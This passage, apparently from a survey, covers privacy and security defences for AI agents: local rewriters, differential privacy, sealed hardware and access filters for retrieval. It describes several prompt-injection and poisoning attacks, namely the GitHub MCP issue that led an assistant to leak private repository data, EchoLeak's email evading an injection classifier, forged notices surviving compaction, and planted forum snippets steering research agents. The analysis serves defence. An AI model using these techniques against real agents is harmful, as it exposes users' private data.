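The researchers tested the consequences with Progent, in which a language model writes the rules for tool calls from the user's request. They changed Progent to write new rules for every request, because the agent completed only 7 of 60 follow-up tasks when the rules were fixed at the start, compared with 41 when they were rewritten. The new rules allowed the attacker's transfer in 17 of 30 banking runs with a summary in the user's position, and in none of 28 runs with the same summaries presented as tool results.

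When summarizing, more capable models often marked injected instructions as suspicious but rarely marked false data. In one test, the user gave an account number for the rent, and an attacker's notice gave a different one. After compaction, rules based on the summary allowed the attacker's account in 91% of cases with one rule-writing model and 59% with another, while rules based on the user's own words never allowed it.

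A better summary cannot fully solve this. Let p_L be the chance that a check accepts an account number from a genuine notice, and p_A the chance that it accepts one from a forged notice. Fei and colleagues prove that, if the check sees only text with no record of who wrote it,

p_L − p_A ≤ TV,

where TV, the total variation distance, measures how well anyone could tell the two kinds of text apart. It runs from 0 (not at all) to 1 (perfectly). If TV is 0.1 and the check accepts 95% of genuine notices, it must also accept at least 85% of forged ones. A forger who copies the genuine format exactly brings TV down to 0.

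Their remedy is to preserve the record of who wrote what. The software attaches a cryptographic tag to each of the user's messages when it arrives and keeps those messages unchanged through compaction. The agent still reads the summary, but the part of the system that writes the rules receives only the user's tagged messages and the output of any tools the company has chosen to trust. If a message is missing, altered or out of order, the agent cannot call any tools. With this protection, no attack succeeded in 40 attacked runs. It does not help when the user asks the agent to pay whatever account a document names, because the system must then also authenticate the document's source.

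## Experiments with small local models that decide what a remote model sees

A hospital that wants to use a frontier model without handing over patient records can run a small model on its own machines and have it write the prompts. The hospital trusts the small model with everything and distrusts the frontier model only because an outside company runs it. Most of the experiments assume this company is honest but curious, meaning it answers properly but may store and study every query.

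### PAPILLON and its four-point gain

*PAPILLON* (Siyan, Raghuram and colleagues, 2024) called this task privacy-conscious delegation. A system with a trusted weak model and an untrusted strong model receives a query that contains private information. It should answer as well as the strong model would, while revealing as little of that information as possible to the strong model.

PAPILLON does this in three steps:

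1. The local model reads q and writes a new prompt, q′.
2. The remote model answers q′.
3. The local model reads the original query and the remote answer, and writes the final response.

The leakage score for a query is the share of its private items that appear in the new prompt:

Leak = (private items found in q′) / n.

The test set was 237 real messages to ChatGPT, mostly about job applications, company finances and emails. The local model was Llama-3.1-8B and the remote one was GPT-4o-mini. Quality is the percentage of responses that a judge considered at least as good as ChatGPT's original response.

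| What the remote model receives | Quality | Leakage |
|---|---|---|
| The original query | 88.2 | 100 |
| The query with private items blacked out | 77.2 | 0 |
| PAPILLON's prompt | 85.5 | 7.5 |
| Nothing, because the local model answers alone | 81.5 | 0 |

PAPILLON clearly beats blacking out names. But it beats the local model alone by only four points, or about nine queries, and using the local model alone leaks nothing. The leakage score is the share of private items that leaked. Queries had about three private items each, so a score of 7.5% could mean that anywhere from 7.5% to about 22% of queries leaked something.

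Both scores come from language models acting as judges. When Siyan and colleagues compared the quality judge with people on 50 pairs of responses, the two agreed only 65% to 71% of the time, which is weak support for a four-point difference. The leakage judge did better: most participants accepted its score in 86% of cases.

These results are now mainly of historical interest because both models are several generations old, and a current local model could probably answer more of the queries alone. The later work has improved on PAPILLON by using broader definitions of what is private, training the rewriting model instead of only searching for good prompts, and finishing some calculations locally on the real data.

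### From names to what the task needs

A message can identify someone without naming them. If a city has a million people, 1% of them are nurses and 3% of those nurses are pregnant, then "a pregnant nurse" in that city could be any of 300 people. The number of people who fit a description is its k-anonymity, and each added detail lowers it.

Siyan, Yu and Hirschberg (2026), in *Beyond Direct Identifiers*, tuned PAPILLON to increase k, using a language model's estimates of population statistics. They left the original leakage score out of the tuning target, and leakage rose for four of the six local models, including from 24.9% to 35.8% with Llama-3.1-8B and from 35.1% to 66.5% with Qwen-2.5-7B. Tuning a rewriter to improve one privacy measure can evidently worsen another that the target omits.

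The estimates of k are also hard to trust. When the system can't estimate a figure, it assumes a population of 400 million, so a very good score may only mean the estimate failed. The untuned Llama pipeline leaked 17.4% in the 2024 tests, on the same queries and with the same remote model. The follow-up used a newer judge, which may explain part of the difference.

Whether a detail should go out also depends on the question. A peanut allergy matters if the user wants ideas for snacks, but not if they want a script to rename files. Huang, Cao and Yang (2026), in *Need to Know*, built a benchmark of 3,167 requests around this distinction, marking which details each task needs and which sensitive ones it doesn't. They then trained a rewriter with 3 billion parameters using the reward

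R = −1 if the new prompt reveals any unneeded sensitive detail;
R = ρ^α × L otherwise.

Here ρ is the share of needed details the prompt keeps, α is between 0 and 1, and L falls below 1 if the prompt is too long. One leak therefore cancels all credit for usefulness. The rewriter raised average utility by up to 10.1 points over systems that ran entirely on the device.

That is a better objective than PAPILLON's, which let good answers compensate for leaks. However, Huang and colleagues use the same two kinds of text comparison to detect leaks in training and in testing, so the rewriter may have learned wordings that both comparisons miss. The principle also allows some serious disclosures, such as the name of a rare disease, which the remote model needs when a doctor asks how to treat it.

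### Hiding the purpose of a request

*Ask Without Telling* (Wang, Li and colleagues, September 2026) points out that a request can reveal a secret even after all the names and figures are removed. For example, a health authority that asks how to divide scarce medical supplies among hospitals may reveal an outbreak. The paper's system, PriCon, therefore disguises the task itself. The rewrites below come from the paper, with small invented figures.

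Suppose the authority has three ventilators for two hospitals. Hospital A needs two and has priority weight 3, while Hospital B needs three and has weight 2. If the harm grows with the square of the shortage, the authority wants whole numbers a and b that minimise

3(2 − a)² + 2(3 − b)², with a + b ≤ 3.

1. **Private request.** The authority asks its local model how to share the ventilators, and supplies the hospitals' names and the figures.
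2. **Rewritten query.** The local model asks how to allocate a limited stock of graphics processors among model-training jobs with different priorities and demands. Placeholders replace all the figures.
3. **Remote answer.** The remote model describes a method: take the jobs one at a time, keep track of the processors already assigned, try every allocation that fits, and keep the one with the lowest total cost.
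4. **Local reconstruction.** The local system turns jobs back into hospitals and processors back into ventilators, fills in the figures and runs the method. Giving A zero, one or two ventilators and B the rest costs 12, 5 or 8, so A gets one and B gets two.

The company learns nothing about hospitals from this query, but it can still see that someone is ranking claimants for a scarce resource. When PriCon disguised only the setting, the remote model identified the type of task on its first guess in 31% to 59% of cases.

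PriCon can also hide the type of task by rewriting the allocation as a search for the shortest route through a network, so the remote model sees only a question about routing data. Each stage of the network stands for a hospital, each point for the number of ventilators handed out so far, and the length of each link for the harm from a shortage. The shortest route goes from 0 to 1 to 3, has a length of 3 + 2 = 5, and gives the same allocation.

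Wang and colleagues tested this on 100 tasks by asking the remote model to guess the real task from the whole exchange. When only names and figures were removed, the model identified the setting on its first guess at least 93% of the time. With the full disguise, it never identified the setting or the type of task on its first guess, and it succeeded at most 2% of the time with five guesses. Hiding the real request among 20 decoys was less effective than PriCon and used about five times as many tokens.

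The guesser had only the text, whereas a real provider also knows whose account sent it and when. A provider might be suspicious if a health authority suddenly started asking about network routing, especially if flu cases were rising that week. An analyst who knew about PriCon could also list the practical problems that turn into this kind of route search, but the experiment doesn't appear to have included one.

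Every method in the comparison solved 100% of the tasks, so the benchmark was too easy to reveal any loss of quality from the disguise. PriCon used roughly three to five times as many tokens as asking directly. One of its three "local" models was GPT-4o-mini, which runs only on OpenAI's servers, so that part of the test doesn't show what a hospital could run itself. The method also can't disguise a question such as what a particular drug does, because the answer depends on the drug.

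### Splitting a question into parts

A local model can also ask several general questions and put the answers together itself. In April 2026, Yao, Shi and colleagues (2026), in *Beyond Local vs. External*, trained one model to write such sub-queries and another to reconstruct the original question from them. The two took turns learning. The reward for the first was

R = α × (similarity of the final answer to a reference answer) − β × (similarity of the reconstructed question to the original),

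where α and β set the balance between quality and privacy.

In the biomedical example, the private question is how the Wnt pathway and the protein β-catenin affect cartilage cells. The local model sends the remote model three questions: how binding at a receptor can stop a cell from breaking down certain proteins, how proteins that can't bind DNA affect genes, and how stabilised proteins enter the nucleus. It then combines the answers with its information about the original question and gives a good account of the pathway in cartilage.

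The sub-queries hid the type of cell, but they led the remote model to the pathway they were supposed to conceal. Its answer to the first sub-query included Wnt and β-catenin as an example.

The overall results are similarly modest. With a 3-billion-parameter local model, the method closed a little over half the gap in answer quality between the local and remote models on biomedical questions, measured by the longest sequence of words shared with a reference answer. An attacker trying to pick the true source passage from a set of candidates succeeded 18.4% of the time, compared with 19.3% for the next-best defence. Human experts picked the right passage 21.7% of the time. The 0.9-point difference between the two defences offers little extra protection, although Yao and colleagues call the reduction in leakage significant.

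All the sub-queries went to one company. Sending them to several would probably hide more, provided the companies didn't compare notes.

### Changing the numbers and recovering the answer

*RECAST* (Pei, Chen and colleagues, October 2026) deals with numerical questions about charts and recordings. The system first turns the chart or recording into text on the user's own machine. A local model with 4 billion parameters then changes the names and the topic, and ordinary code replaces the numbers. Finally, the system produces a new chart or recording from the altered text, because some remote services accept only those formats.

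Suppose a chart shows 240 admissions at one clinic and 180 at another, and the user wants the difference. ReCast might change the clinics to shops and the figures to 310 and 205. The remote model returns a short program, 310 − 205, with both numbers marked as substitutes. Local code restores the original numbers and computes 240 − 180 = 60.

ReCast answered 75.1% of 4,000 test questions correctly, which is 92.4% of the accuracy the same remote model reached with the original data. A model judge found leaked content in 7.95% of requests, compared with 39.75% for the same local model without fine-tuning. On charts, ReCast scored 70.2%, while a local model working alone scored 62.8%.

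The 7.95% is not comparable to PAPILLON's 7.5%, because one counts requests and the other counts private items. ReCast's audit covers only what goes to the model that solves the problem, but other remote services that help draw the chart or produce the speech also receive the rewritten content.

Some information remains even when the rewriting works perfectly. ReCast leaves most whole numbers from 0 to 15 unchanged, keeps values of similar size in the same order, and preserves the gaps between related years. A chart of three deaths on one ward and nine on another would still show three and nine. Pei and colleagues acknowledge that the checks before release give no formal privacy guarantee.

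### What a privacy budget costs

A low leakage rate applies only to the queries tested and the model that judged them or the attack used, whereas a guarantee would have to cover every attacker and every permitted query. Even if PriCon's true count of leaks was zero in 100 independent tasks, the underlying rate against the same guesser could be as high as about 3%. A better guesser might succeed much more often.

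Differential privacy offers one. It adds randomness so that no single protected item affects the output very much. For a random procedure M, any two inputs D and D′ that differ in one protected item, and any set S of possible outputs, it requires

Pr[M(D) ∈ S] ≤ e^ε × Pr[M(D′) ∈ S] + δ.

A smaller ε means stronger privacy, and δ is a small allowance for exceptions. When δ is zero, seeing the output can change any attacker's odds between two possible values of the item by a factor of at most e^ε, or about 11% when ε = 0.1.

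Gaikwad (2025), in *AVEC*, applies this to prompts. Software on the device looks for names, identifiers and dates, and replaces each one at random from a list of k possibilities. The true value survives with probability

e^ε / (e^ε + k − 1),

and each of the others is equally likely to replace it.

| ε | True value survives, k = 8 | True value survives, k = 64 |
|---|---|---|
| 0.1 | 13.6% | 1.7% |
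| 1 | 28.0% | 4.1% |
| 5 | 95.5% | 70.2% |

With strong privacy, the remote model therefore sees the wrong item nearly every time. This hardly matters for a name in a letter, because the local system can put the real name back, but it is a serious problem for a drug, because the remote model would give advice about the wrong one.

Privacy loss also accumulates. Under the simplest accounting, the total ε is the sum over all protected items and queries. In Gaikwad's simulation, each user had a total budget of between 1 and 2 for ten queries. Spreading a budget of 2 over ten queries with one protected item each allows ε = 0.2 per item, and the true value would be kept only 1.9% of the time in a list of 64. Once the budget runs out, the system has to answer locally or not at all.

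AVEC sets the budget for each query by the formula

ε = ε_base × S × (1 − C) × F + noise,

where S is the query's sensitivity, C is the local model's confidence, and F falls as the session goes on. As written, a more sensitive query gets a larger ε and so weaker protection, which seems to be the wrong way round. The noise is another problem. It has a scale of 30 in the simulation, while the rest of the formula never exceeds 0.1, so the noise would swamp the calculation. The simulation used no real language models either, so AVEC is better evidence about the mathematics than about a working product.

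Its guarantee also covers only the items that the software finds. If a prompt calls a patient "the mayor's youngest daughter" and the detector looks for names, the phrase is sent unchanged. The decision to consult the remote model can also reveal information. Gaikwad proves that a fixed rule for making that decision cannot satisfy differential privacy if changing one protected item can change the result, so the decision needs randomness too.

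### Rules that code can enforce on a rewriter

A prompt based on a confidential record inherits the record's label, so a strict policy check would block it. Sending it anyway is declassification, and the small model decides what is safe to release. The rest of the system therefore has to trust the small model's decision, whereas it never trusts the output of a quarantined model.

Code can reliably block an exact patient number or limit the length of a prompt. But it can't recognise every paraphrase, and even a short prompt can contain a diagnosis. The rewriter may also read a document written by a stranger, which exposes it to the kind of attack that has defeated models used as filters. The rewriting experiments did not test such attacks.

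Making the rewriter choose from a fixed list would limit much more firmly what each query can reveal. If a hospital approved 256 general questions in advance and code blocked all others, each query could carry at most log₂(256) = 8 bits. The rewriter could not copy a patient's record into one prompt, although eight bits can still identify one of 256 diagnoses. The list would also exclude most of the unusual questions for which the hospital wanted a frontier model.

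The strongest rule is still to have ordinary code remove everything that must not reach the remote model before the local rewriter reads the text. ReCast does something similar with numbers, which code replaces after the model has rewritten the text. But that protection depends on the code finding every number, and it doesn't cover the small numbers that ReCast deliberately keeps.

### A capable model in a sealed environment

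The hospital could let a capable model see the data but prevent the company that hosts the model from seeing it. Shumailov, Ramage and colleagues (2025) propose in *Trusted Machine Learning Models Unlock Private Inference* that a model in a sealed environment could act as a trusted intermediary between parties who don't trust one another. The parties agree on the model, the prompt, and the permitted inputs and outputs. The model must keep nothing afterwards, which was also Lampson's first rule for confinement.

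In one example from Shumailov and colleagues, a regulator wants to know whether a business stores private data insecurely, and the business wants to keep its code secret. The model reads the code and may output only YES or NO. An ordinary program can enforce that restriction, so even a badly behaved model's answer reveals at most one bit per run. The answer could still be wrong, and Shumailov and colleagues describe the overall guarantees as heuristic and weaker than those of cryptography.

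In *Trusted Model Environment for Private Semantic Computations* (September 2026), Duddu and He built a working version that runs open models with 7 to 9 billion parameters inside secure hardware, which encrypts memory and isolates the program from the rest of the machine. The hardware can also sign a statement, called an attestation, identifying the program and model it is running.

Secure hardware alone did not protect the data, because the models revealed it in their answers. In a test where outsiders asked questions about a private document, attack prompts extracted sensitive details from the three unprotected models in 59–100% of cases. Duddu and He then trained the models to resist such prompts and added a step that checks each answer for leaks and another that rewrites any answer containing one. Leakage fell to 1–3%. For prompts that asked for the details indirectly, it fell from 49–66%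 to 2–5%.

These results are good, but allowing free-text answers gives up the main advantage of the YES-or-NO design, because models again decide what gets out. Qwen3-8B both looks for leaks during operation and judges paraphrased leaks in the evaluation, so it could miss the same ones both times. The leak check also raised the time for an answer from two or three seconds to about 11, or about 40 if the answer needed rewriting. The attestations added almost no time.

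A hospital asking about its own records may not need those steps, because the answer goes only to the hospital. It mainly needs the sealed hardware, which added less than 7% to running costs in earlier benchmarks. For a hospital with no model of its own, sealed hardware seems a better choice than rewriting every query, because the model can work from the original question.

The hospital then has to trust the chip makers. Duddu and He exclude most attacks that exploit physical side effects such as power use, although they pad answers to a fixed length so that timing reveals less. They ran their models on an Nvidia H100, which Shumailov and colleagues say lacks confidential memory and a guaranteed way to erase memory. Full verification also requires publishing the model and its software. Companies that sell closed frontier models may refuse, so the hospital might have to use an open model.

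### Auditing a small model

People often suggest small models as gatekeepers because they should be easier to audit, but the audits in these experiments mostly checked outputs. For PAPILLON, five people reviewed the leakage scores for 50 rewritten prompts. For ReCast, three of its authors labelled 400 examples, and the judge's labels matched the majority's on 91.5% of them. ReCast also keeps a text version of each request before and after rewriting, so the changes are fairly easy to see. None of this work examined a rewriter's internals to find out what it might reveal in other cases.

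Duddu and He's system uses attestation for a different kind of audit. Its signed record lets an outsider confirm that an approved model produced a particular answer from particular inputs, but not that the answer was safe to release. AVEC's weaker version records only a digest of the privacy settings. Gaikwad proves that such a digest cannot establish differential privacy, since two programs can have the same settings and treat the data differently.

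The local models are also large by the standards of computer security. Anderson thought an operating system of the early 1970s was too large to verify, and these rewriters have billions of parameters. A smaller model could be easier to analyze but less reliable. In the PAPILLON tests, the smallest model, with 1 billion parameters, leaked 39.3% of private items after tuning, compared with 7.5% for the best model, which had 8 billion. But a 22-billion-parameter model leaked 27.4%, so a larger model isn't automatically safer. That model was noticeably better at hiding people's names than nationalities or company names, and it did worse with text that the user wanted translated. A hospital would have to test for such weaknesses on its own records.

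## Retrieval modules as gatekeepers: access rules and poisoned documents

A retrieval module can control access more easily than a local rewriter, because ordinary code can admit or reject whole documents by a fixed rule, while a rewriter has to judge which words are safe to send. The frontier model is untrusted here because it may reveal anything it reads, whether by mistake, because an attacker prompts it to, or for reasons of its own.

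### Where a rule can act

*SoK* (Bodea, Meisenbacher and colleagues, 2026), a review of 72 papers on privacy in retrieval systems, describes three stages in these systems. In indexing, software splits documents into passages, and an embedding model turns each passage into a vector, a list of numbers. Passages with similar meanings get vectors that are close together. In retrieval, the software also turns the user's question into a vector and finds the k nearest passages. In generation, it pastes those passages into the prompt, and the model answers.

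None of these stages checks who is asking. *Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI* (2026) gives the example of an insurance officer who may see claim 4471 but not claim 4472. If both claims are about burst pipes, a search for burst pipes will probably return both. Arceo and Narsing (2026), in *Securing the Agent*, define the correct result for a user u and a question q as

{d ∈ D : relevance(q, d) > θ and P(u, d) = permit},

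where D is the collection, θ is the lowest acceptable relevance and P is the access policy. An ordinary search applies only the first condition. Code can apply the second at several points:

| Where the rule acts | How it works | Main drawback |
|---|---|---|
| Indexing | Each group of readers has a separate collection | Storage and upkeep grow with the number of groups |
| The search itself | The search covers only passages whose tags match the user's permissions | A change of policy may mean retagging much of the collection |
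| After the search | Code drops forbidden passages before it builds the prompt | The database has already released them, and too few results may remain |
| The finished answer | Code or another model removes forbidden text | The model has already read it |

### Why filtering first gives a guarantee

If the search covers only documents that the user may read, the context depends only on the question and those documents. Rewriting or deleting every forbidden document would not change the text the model receives. This property is called noninterference, and it holds even for a model that is trying to leak. The model may still repeat things it learned in training, which no retrieval rule can prevent. An approximate search through a shared index can weaken noninterference a little, because forbidden passages may affect which permitted ones the search finds. Separate collections avoid this.

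Filtering after the search also keeps forbidden text out of the context, but the forbidden documents can still affect what the user gets. Suppose the software needs five passages and fetches 15. If 11 of them are forbidden, only four remain. *Bounded Provisional Visibility* (2026) shows that software that fetches α times as many passages as it needs runs short when more than 1 − 1/α of the fetched passages are forbidden. In this example, α is 3 and the threshold is two-thirds. An employee who asks about redundancies at one office and gets unusually few results might guess that hidden documents exist.

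Arceo and Narsing of Red Hat tested filtering in OGX, an open-source framework for agents. They assume that the model may leak any text it receives, so the code must enforce permissions before it builds the context. OGX tags each document with its owner when indexing it. When a user asks a question, OGX first checks whether that user may search the collection, then filters the individual passages. They compared retrieval with and without this filter, and with the agent loop on the server or on the user's side. Without the filter, 98–100% of test queries returned another customer's data. The filter eliminated these leaks and added negligible delay.

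Correct code should produce the zero, so that result mainly confirms that the filter worked. The 98–100% is more informative because it shows how little relevance ranking separates customers who share a collection. But the test queries were presumably written to find leaks, so everyday questions would probably cause fewer.

*Protection Is Not One Event* (Liu, Wang et al., 2026), a survey of 118 defences, also concludes that early checks are much safer than late ones. It cites a test of row-level security, a database feature that hides forbidden rows from every query, which cut leakage between customers from 0.2% to zero over 1,000 queries. In another study it cites, searching first and filtering afterwards exposed unauthorised passages in 86.1% of queries. If the filter removed those passages before the software built the prompt, the model never saw them, so the figure may show how often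 safety depended on the filter, not how often the filter failed.

Replacing such a filter with a model can make access decisions less accurate. In another study from the survey, an AI filter that judged permissions by the user's role scored 0.89 on F1, a measure of accuracy that runs from 0 to 1, while a simple fixed filter scored 0.93 to 0.94.

### Asking the model to keep a secret

Some systems put restricted text in the context and tell the model not to share it. *GraphSteal* (2026) tested such an instruction and found that carefully written prompts could override it. A long stretch of retrieved text after the instruction may weaken it further. Better models won't necessarily help, since *LeakDojo* compared fourteen models and found that those better at following instructions tended to leak more, presumably because they also follow an attacker's instructions better.

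Current models can be good at judging access when the forbidden text is not already in front of them. In *DEPUTYBENCH* (2026), agents had to work out whether they were authorised to read something. On twelve tasks with restricted access, GPT-6.2 Astra had a pass rate of 86.1% unaided and 100% with a general checklist. This kind of judgement is useful where no written permission settles the matter, but a perfect score on twelve tasks does not guarantee that the model will judge the next one correctly. *Permit* (2026), which adjusts a model's internal activations to suit the user's permissions, likewise presents its method as an addition to ordinary access control.

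Checking the final answer doesn't solve the problem either. Liu and colleagues tested code that blacks out short sequences of text matching a protected source. Word-for-word copying of longer passages fell to zero, but an attacker who could adapt over three queries still recovered 48.3% of the hidden facts from Qwen3-8B. The figure was 3.3% after one query, so a single-query test would have greatly overstated the protection.

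### What the guarantee depends on

The permissions have to be right. When 12.5% of the labels were missing and the system let unlabelled documents through, Liu and colleagues found that the model again copied protected text word for word in 9.4% to 12.5% of cases. Rejecting unlabelled documents would have prevented this, but it would also have hidden some that users were entitled to read. Arceo and Narsing also assume that the login system identifies each user's organisation correctly and that the database applies the filters it receives.

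Changes to permissions also have to reach every copy. A check after the search can consult the master list and hide a document almost at once, while a filter inside the index takes effect only when the index picks up the change. Using both therefore makes sense, as the insurance example does, with a separate collection for the most restricted files. Deletion can also be incomplete, because some databases only mark a vector as deleted. Liu and colleagues describe research in which someone with access to the index could reconstruct text from such vectors until the operator rebuilt the index.

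Old conversations also hold copies of retrieved text. If an employee loses access to a file on Tuesday, a passage the agent retrieved on Monday may still be in the context. Arceo and Narsing therefore call for checking permissions again at every turn, and the software has to remove anything that fails. Cached tool results need the same treatment.

Finally, the code has to check permissions at every step of a search that leads from one document to another. Thornton (2026), in *Retrieval Pivot Attacks in Hybrid RAG*, studied systems that first find a passage by similarity and then follow links in a knowledge graph, a database of how people, companies and other things are related. A permitted memo might mention a supplier, and the supplier's entry might link to a confidential contract. If the code checks only the memo, the contract enters the model's context. A search by similarity alone would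 not have followed that link.

Even a perfect filter checks only whether this user may read this document. A doctor may be allowed to read a patient's record that the hospital is not allowed to send to an outside company, so a hospital using a remote model needs a second check on whether the company may receive the record. The filter also doesn't control where the model's answer goes. It would not have stopped Alex's reply to Marco, because Alex was allowed to read both emails.

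### Planted documents that anyone may read

Access rules don't protect against a false document that the user is allowed to read. According to *Towards Secure Retrieval-Augmented Generation* (Mu, Hu and colleagues, 2026), a planted text must be similar enough to the question for the search to return it and persuasive enough to change the answer. Researchers have paid little attention to prevention. Among 135 works, *A Survey of Secure Retrieval-Augmented Generation* (Xu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) counts 42 that mainly attack a collection before the search and only four that mainly defend it at that point.

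The public web is especially exposed to poisoning because anyone can add to parts of it. *Deep-Research Agents Can Be Poisoned via User-Generated Content* (Zhang, Triedman and Shmatikov, May 2026) studies agents that run many web searches and write a report with citations. An attacker can't predict the searches, but the same forum threads and videos keep appearing in the results. One agent retrieved the same YouTube video for all 11 questions in a group about comparing products.

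The researchers put 176 questions on 11 topics to three open-source agents, all using GPT-4o-mini. For each agent and topic, they picked the user-written page that came up most often and added about 13 words to its search snippet to promote something that doesn't exist. One addition promoted an invented Mexican restaurant near Austin, which the agent described in its report as "highly recommended". The researchers' software inserted the words into the search results before they reached the agent, without changing any real pages. The table gives the results as percentages.

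| Agent | Runs in which the altered snippet reached the agent | Reports that named the invented item | Reports that named it, counting only runs the snippet reached |
|---|---|---|---|
| Co-STORM | 60.6 | 30.7 | 50.6 |
| STORM | 76.2 | 37.1 | 48.6 |
| OmniThink | 57.4 | 21.7 | 37.8 |

The last column gives the paper's headline range of 38–51%. A user asking one of these questions had a 22–37% chance of getting a poisoned recommendation. Altering three pages raised that chance to 33–46%. It was still 18–31% when the agents read whole Reddit threads and the planted text made up less than 4% of what they retrieved.

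These rates apply to topics where forum advice matters and manipulation is profitable. In a separate test with a more varied set of 460 questions about medical supplements, 10% of reports recommended an invented compound. GPT-4o-mini is also an old, small model, and a current one might be harder to fool. Results already varied by topic. When the altered snippet reached STORM, the system always recommended an invented roadside-assistance service but never an invented cryptocurrency. However, even a very good model has little reason to doubt a plausible restaurant tip.

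Zhang and colleagues counted citations in commercial products rather than attacking the products, which would have meant planting false text on the live web. User-written pages made up 12.1% of citations in Gemini Deep Research and 0.4% in OpenAI Deep Research, so the two products' exposure may differ considerably.

Filters for odd-looking text failed because the planted sentences were more fluent than real forum posts. Blocking eight large sites with user-written content stopped attacks through those sites, and a model judge's average score for the reports fell only from 4.30 to 4.26 out of 5. That small drop hardly supports Zhang and colleagues' conclusion that no defence they tried works without making the reports worse. They reasonably doubt, however, that the score captures what personal experience adds to a report. For medical questions, blocking these sites seems well worth it.

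### Answering from each document separately

When a model reads ten documents together, one planted document can affect how it interprets the other nine. In 2024, Chong Xiang and colleagues introduced RobustRAG, which has the model answer from each passage separately and then combines the answers. A planted passage can completely control its own answer but can't affect the others. The method can therefore provide a certificate, which is a proof that no attack within a stated limit can change the result.

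Suppose, for example, that a system answers questions by a simple vote among the documents it retrieves. A user asks how much notice a contract requires, and the search returns ten documents. Two are planted and give the answer as 60 days. The correct answer is 30 days, but some of the other eight are out of date or don't cover notice.

| Honest votes for 30 days | Honest votes for 60 days | Honest documents with no answer | Result with two planted votes for 60 days |
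|---|---|---|---|
| 8 | 0 | 0 | 30 days wins, 8 to 2 |
| 5 | 2 | 1 | 30 days wins, 5 to 4 |
| 4 | 2 | 2 | 4 to 4, no winner |

If the attacker controls at most m documents, the leading honest answer is safe when

h₁ > h₂ + m,

where h₁ and h₂ are the honest votes for the leading answer and its nearest rival.

The system can't use this rule directly, because it doesn't know which votes are honest. It sees only the totals, v₁ and v₂. Replacing a planted document with an honest one could take a vote from the leader and give it to the rival, which changes the margin by two. The system can therefore certify that the winner would have been the same without the attack if

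v₁ − v₂ > 2m.

With m = 2, a vote of 8 to 2 passes because the margin is 6. A vote of 6 to 3 fails because two of the six votes might come from planted documents, and genuine documents in their place could have made the result 4 to 5.

The certificate assumes that at most m of the retrieved documents are planted. That may be reasonable in a company archive with few authors, but it is much harder to defend on the open web, where posting the same claim in a third thread takes very little effort. With three planted documents, the second row of the table becomes 5 to 5. Votes also have to be counted by source rather than by passage, since one planted page split into three passages would otherwise get three votes. Honest pages that copied the false claim also give it extra votes.

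Within its limit, the certificate guarantees only that the attacker can't change the answer. If most of the honest documents are out of date, the vote will still return the wrong notice period. The method also needs a model call for each document, and it does badly on questions whose answers combine facts from two documents. It suits recommendations poorly too, because the vote that rejects an invented restaurant mentioned on one page would also reject a good one that only one person has written about. People read forums to find places like that.

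Real answers are seldom as simple as "30 days", so RobustRAG doesn't just count identical answers. One version keeps only keywords that appear in enough of the separate answers and has the model write a reply from them. Another combines the separate predictions for each next word. ReliabilityRAG, a successor designed for web search, looks for a large set of documents that don't contradict one another, favoring those with a higher search rank or other signs of reliability. This uses information that a plain vote ignores, but the guarantee still holds only if the attacker corrupts a limited number of documents, and an attacker who can push a page up the rankings gains influence.

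### What a provenance record can establish

A company can also control what enters its collection. Sulpovar, Konsynski and colleagues (2026), in *ContextNest*, describe a system that records who wrote each version of a document, when they wrote it and which version an agent read. Each version n gets a hash, or digest:

hash(n) = SHA-256(hash(n − 1), content, version number, editor, time).

Each hash includes the previous one, so if someone alters an old version, its author or its date, the stored hashes from that point on no longer match. In the stricter of two modes, someone other than the author must approve a document before agents can read it. The default mode makes new documents available at once.

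If an auditor asks why an agent approved a supplier six months ago, the record can show which version of the risk policy the agent read, who wrote it and whether anyone has altered it since. Repeating the search might not show this, because in one test a typical vector index returned different documents for the same question in 80% of 50 cases. In another test, with 30 questions and outdated versions mixed into the collection, ContextNest's selection led to acceptable answers 97% of the time, compared with 90–93% for a keyword search. The difference is only one or two questions, and the first author's company maintains the software, but the case for keeping such a record doesn't really depend on that result.

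The record can't establish that a document is true. If an approver accepts a false risk policy, every hash will still match, and the paper explicitly leaves this case out of scope. The paper also excludes confidentiality and access control, so ContextNest doesn't replace a permission filter. An editor's name in the record proves little if someone else used that editor's account.

The protection against tampering is also limited because the formula uses no secret key. Anyone who can rewrite all the histories and the log that ties them together could compute new hashes that match the altered records. To catch this, an auditor needs an earlier hash stored somewhere the attacker can't reach.

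A reliable list of authors would still help against poisoning. It could supply integrity labels that list possible writers, and a voting system could use it to give each author only one vote. The limit m would then apply to dishonest authors, whom a company can count more easily than dishonest documents. This would help much less on a public forum, where one person can open many accounts.

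## Deployed systems and real incidents

Security researchers have demonstrated these flows in two attacks on widely used products. In both, text from a stranger hijacked an honest model, and private data leaked through an ordinary feature of the product.

### A public issue and a private salary

Anyone can usually open an issue, such as a bug report, on a public GitHub repository. Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) describes how an attacker could use such an issue to extract private data. The user had connected Claude Desktop, Anthropic's desktop assistant, to a GitHub account through an MCP server, a program that offers outside tools to models through a standard called the Model Context Protocol. The account held several private repositories and a public one containing a Pac-Man game.

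A user asked Claude 4 Opus to look at the open issues in a public repository, one of which contained an attacker's instructions. Claude followed them, read the user's private repositories and opened a pull request (a proposed code change) in the public one. The pull request let anyone read about the user's private projects, salary and plan to move to South America.

In terms of labels, the attack had three parts:

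- **Source:** the issue was untrusted and public, while the private repositories were trusted and private.
- **Path:** both entered the same context, and their join is (untrusted, private).
- **Sink:** the pull request was a public channel.

Microsoft uses this attack as an example and gives a rule that would have stopped it: an agent whose context is (untrusted, private) may not post to a public channel. A plain confidentiality rule would also have stopped it, since private data was going to a public place, but Microsoft's rule still lets users publish their own private material when nothing untrusted is in the context.

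Invariant Labs recommends a simpler rule that limits the agent to one repository per session. This would also have stopped the attack, and it needs no labels. But it blocks harmless work across two private repositories, and it doesn't cover a salary taken from a mailbox. Invariant Labs, which offers software for enforcing such rules, says the agent keeps its full functionality within authorised boundaries, but that is true only if the task needs a single repository.

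The GitHub server had no bug to fix, because the agent used permissions that the user had given it. GitHub has since added limits on what the agent can send out and what it can read. In August, GitHub (2025) announced that the server would scan tool calls involving public repositories for secrets such as access tokens, and block them by default. The scan wouldn't detect other private information, such as a salary. In December, GitHub (2025) announced a lockdown mode that restricts content that untrusted contributors add to public repositories.

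### EchoLeak and the image request

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions using their email, files and chats. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, explains how an outsider could steal data from Copilot's context by sending one email:

1. The email addressed its instructions to the employee and never mentioned AI, so Microsoft's injection classifier let it through.
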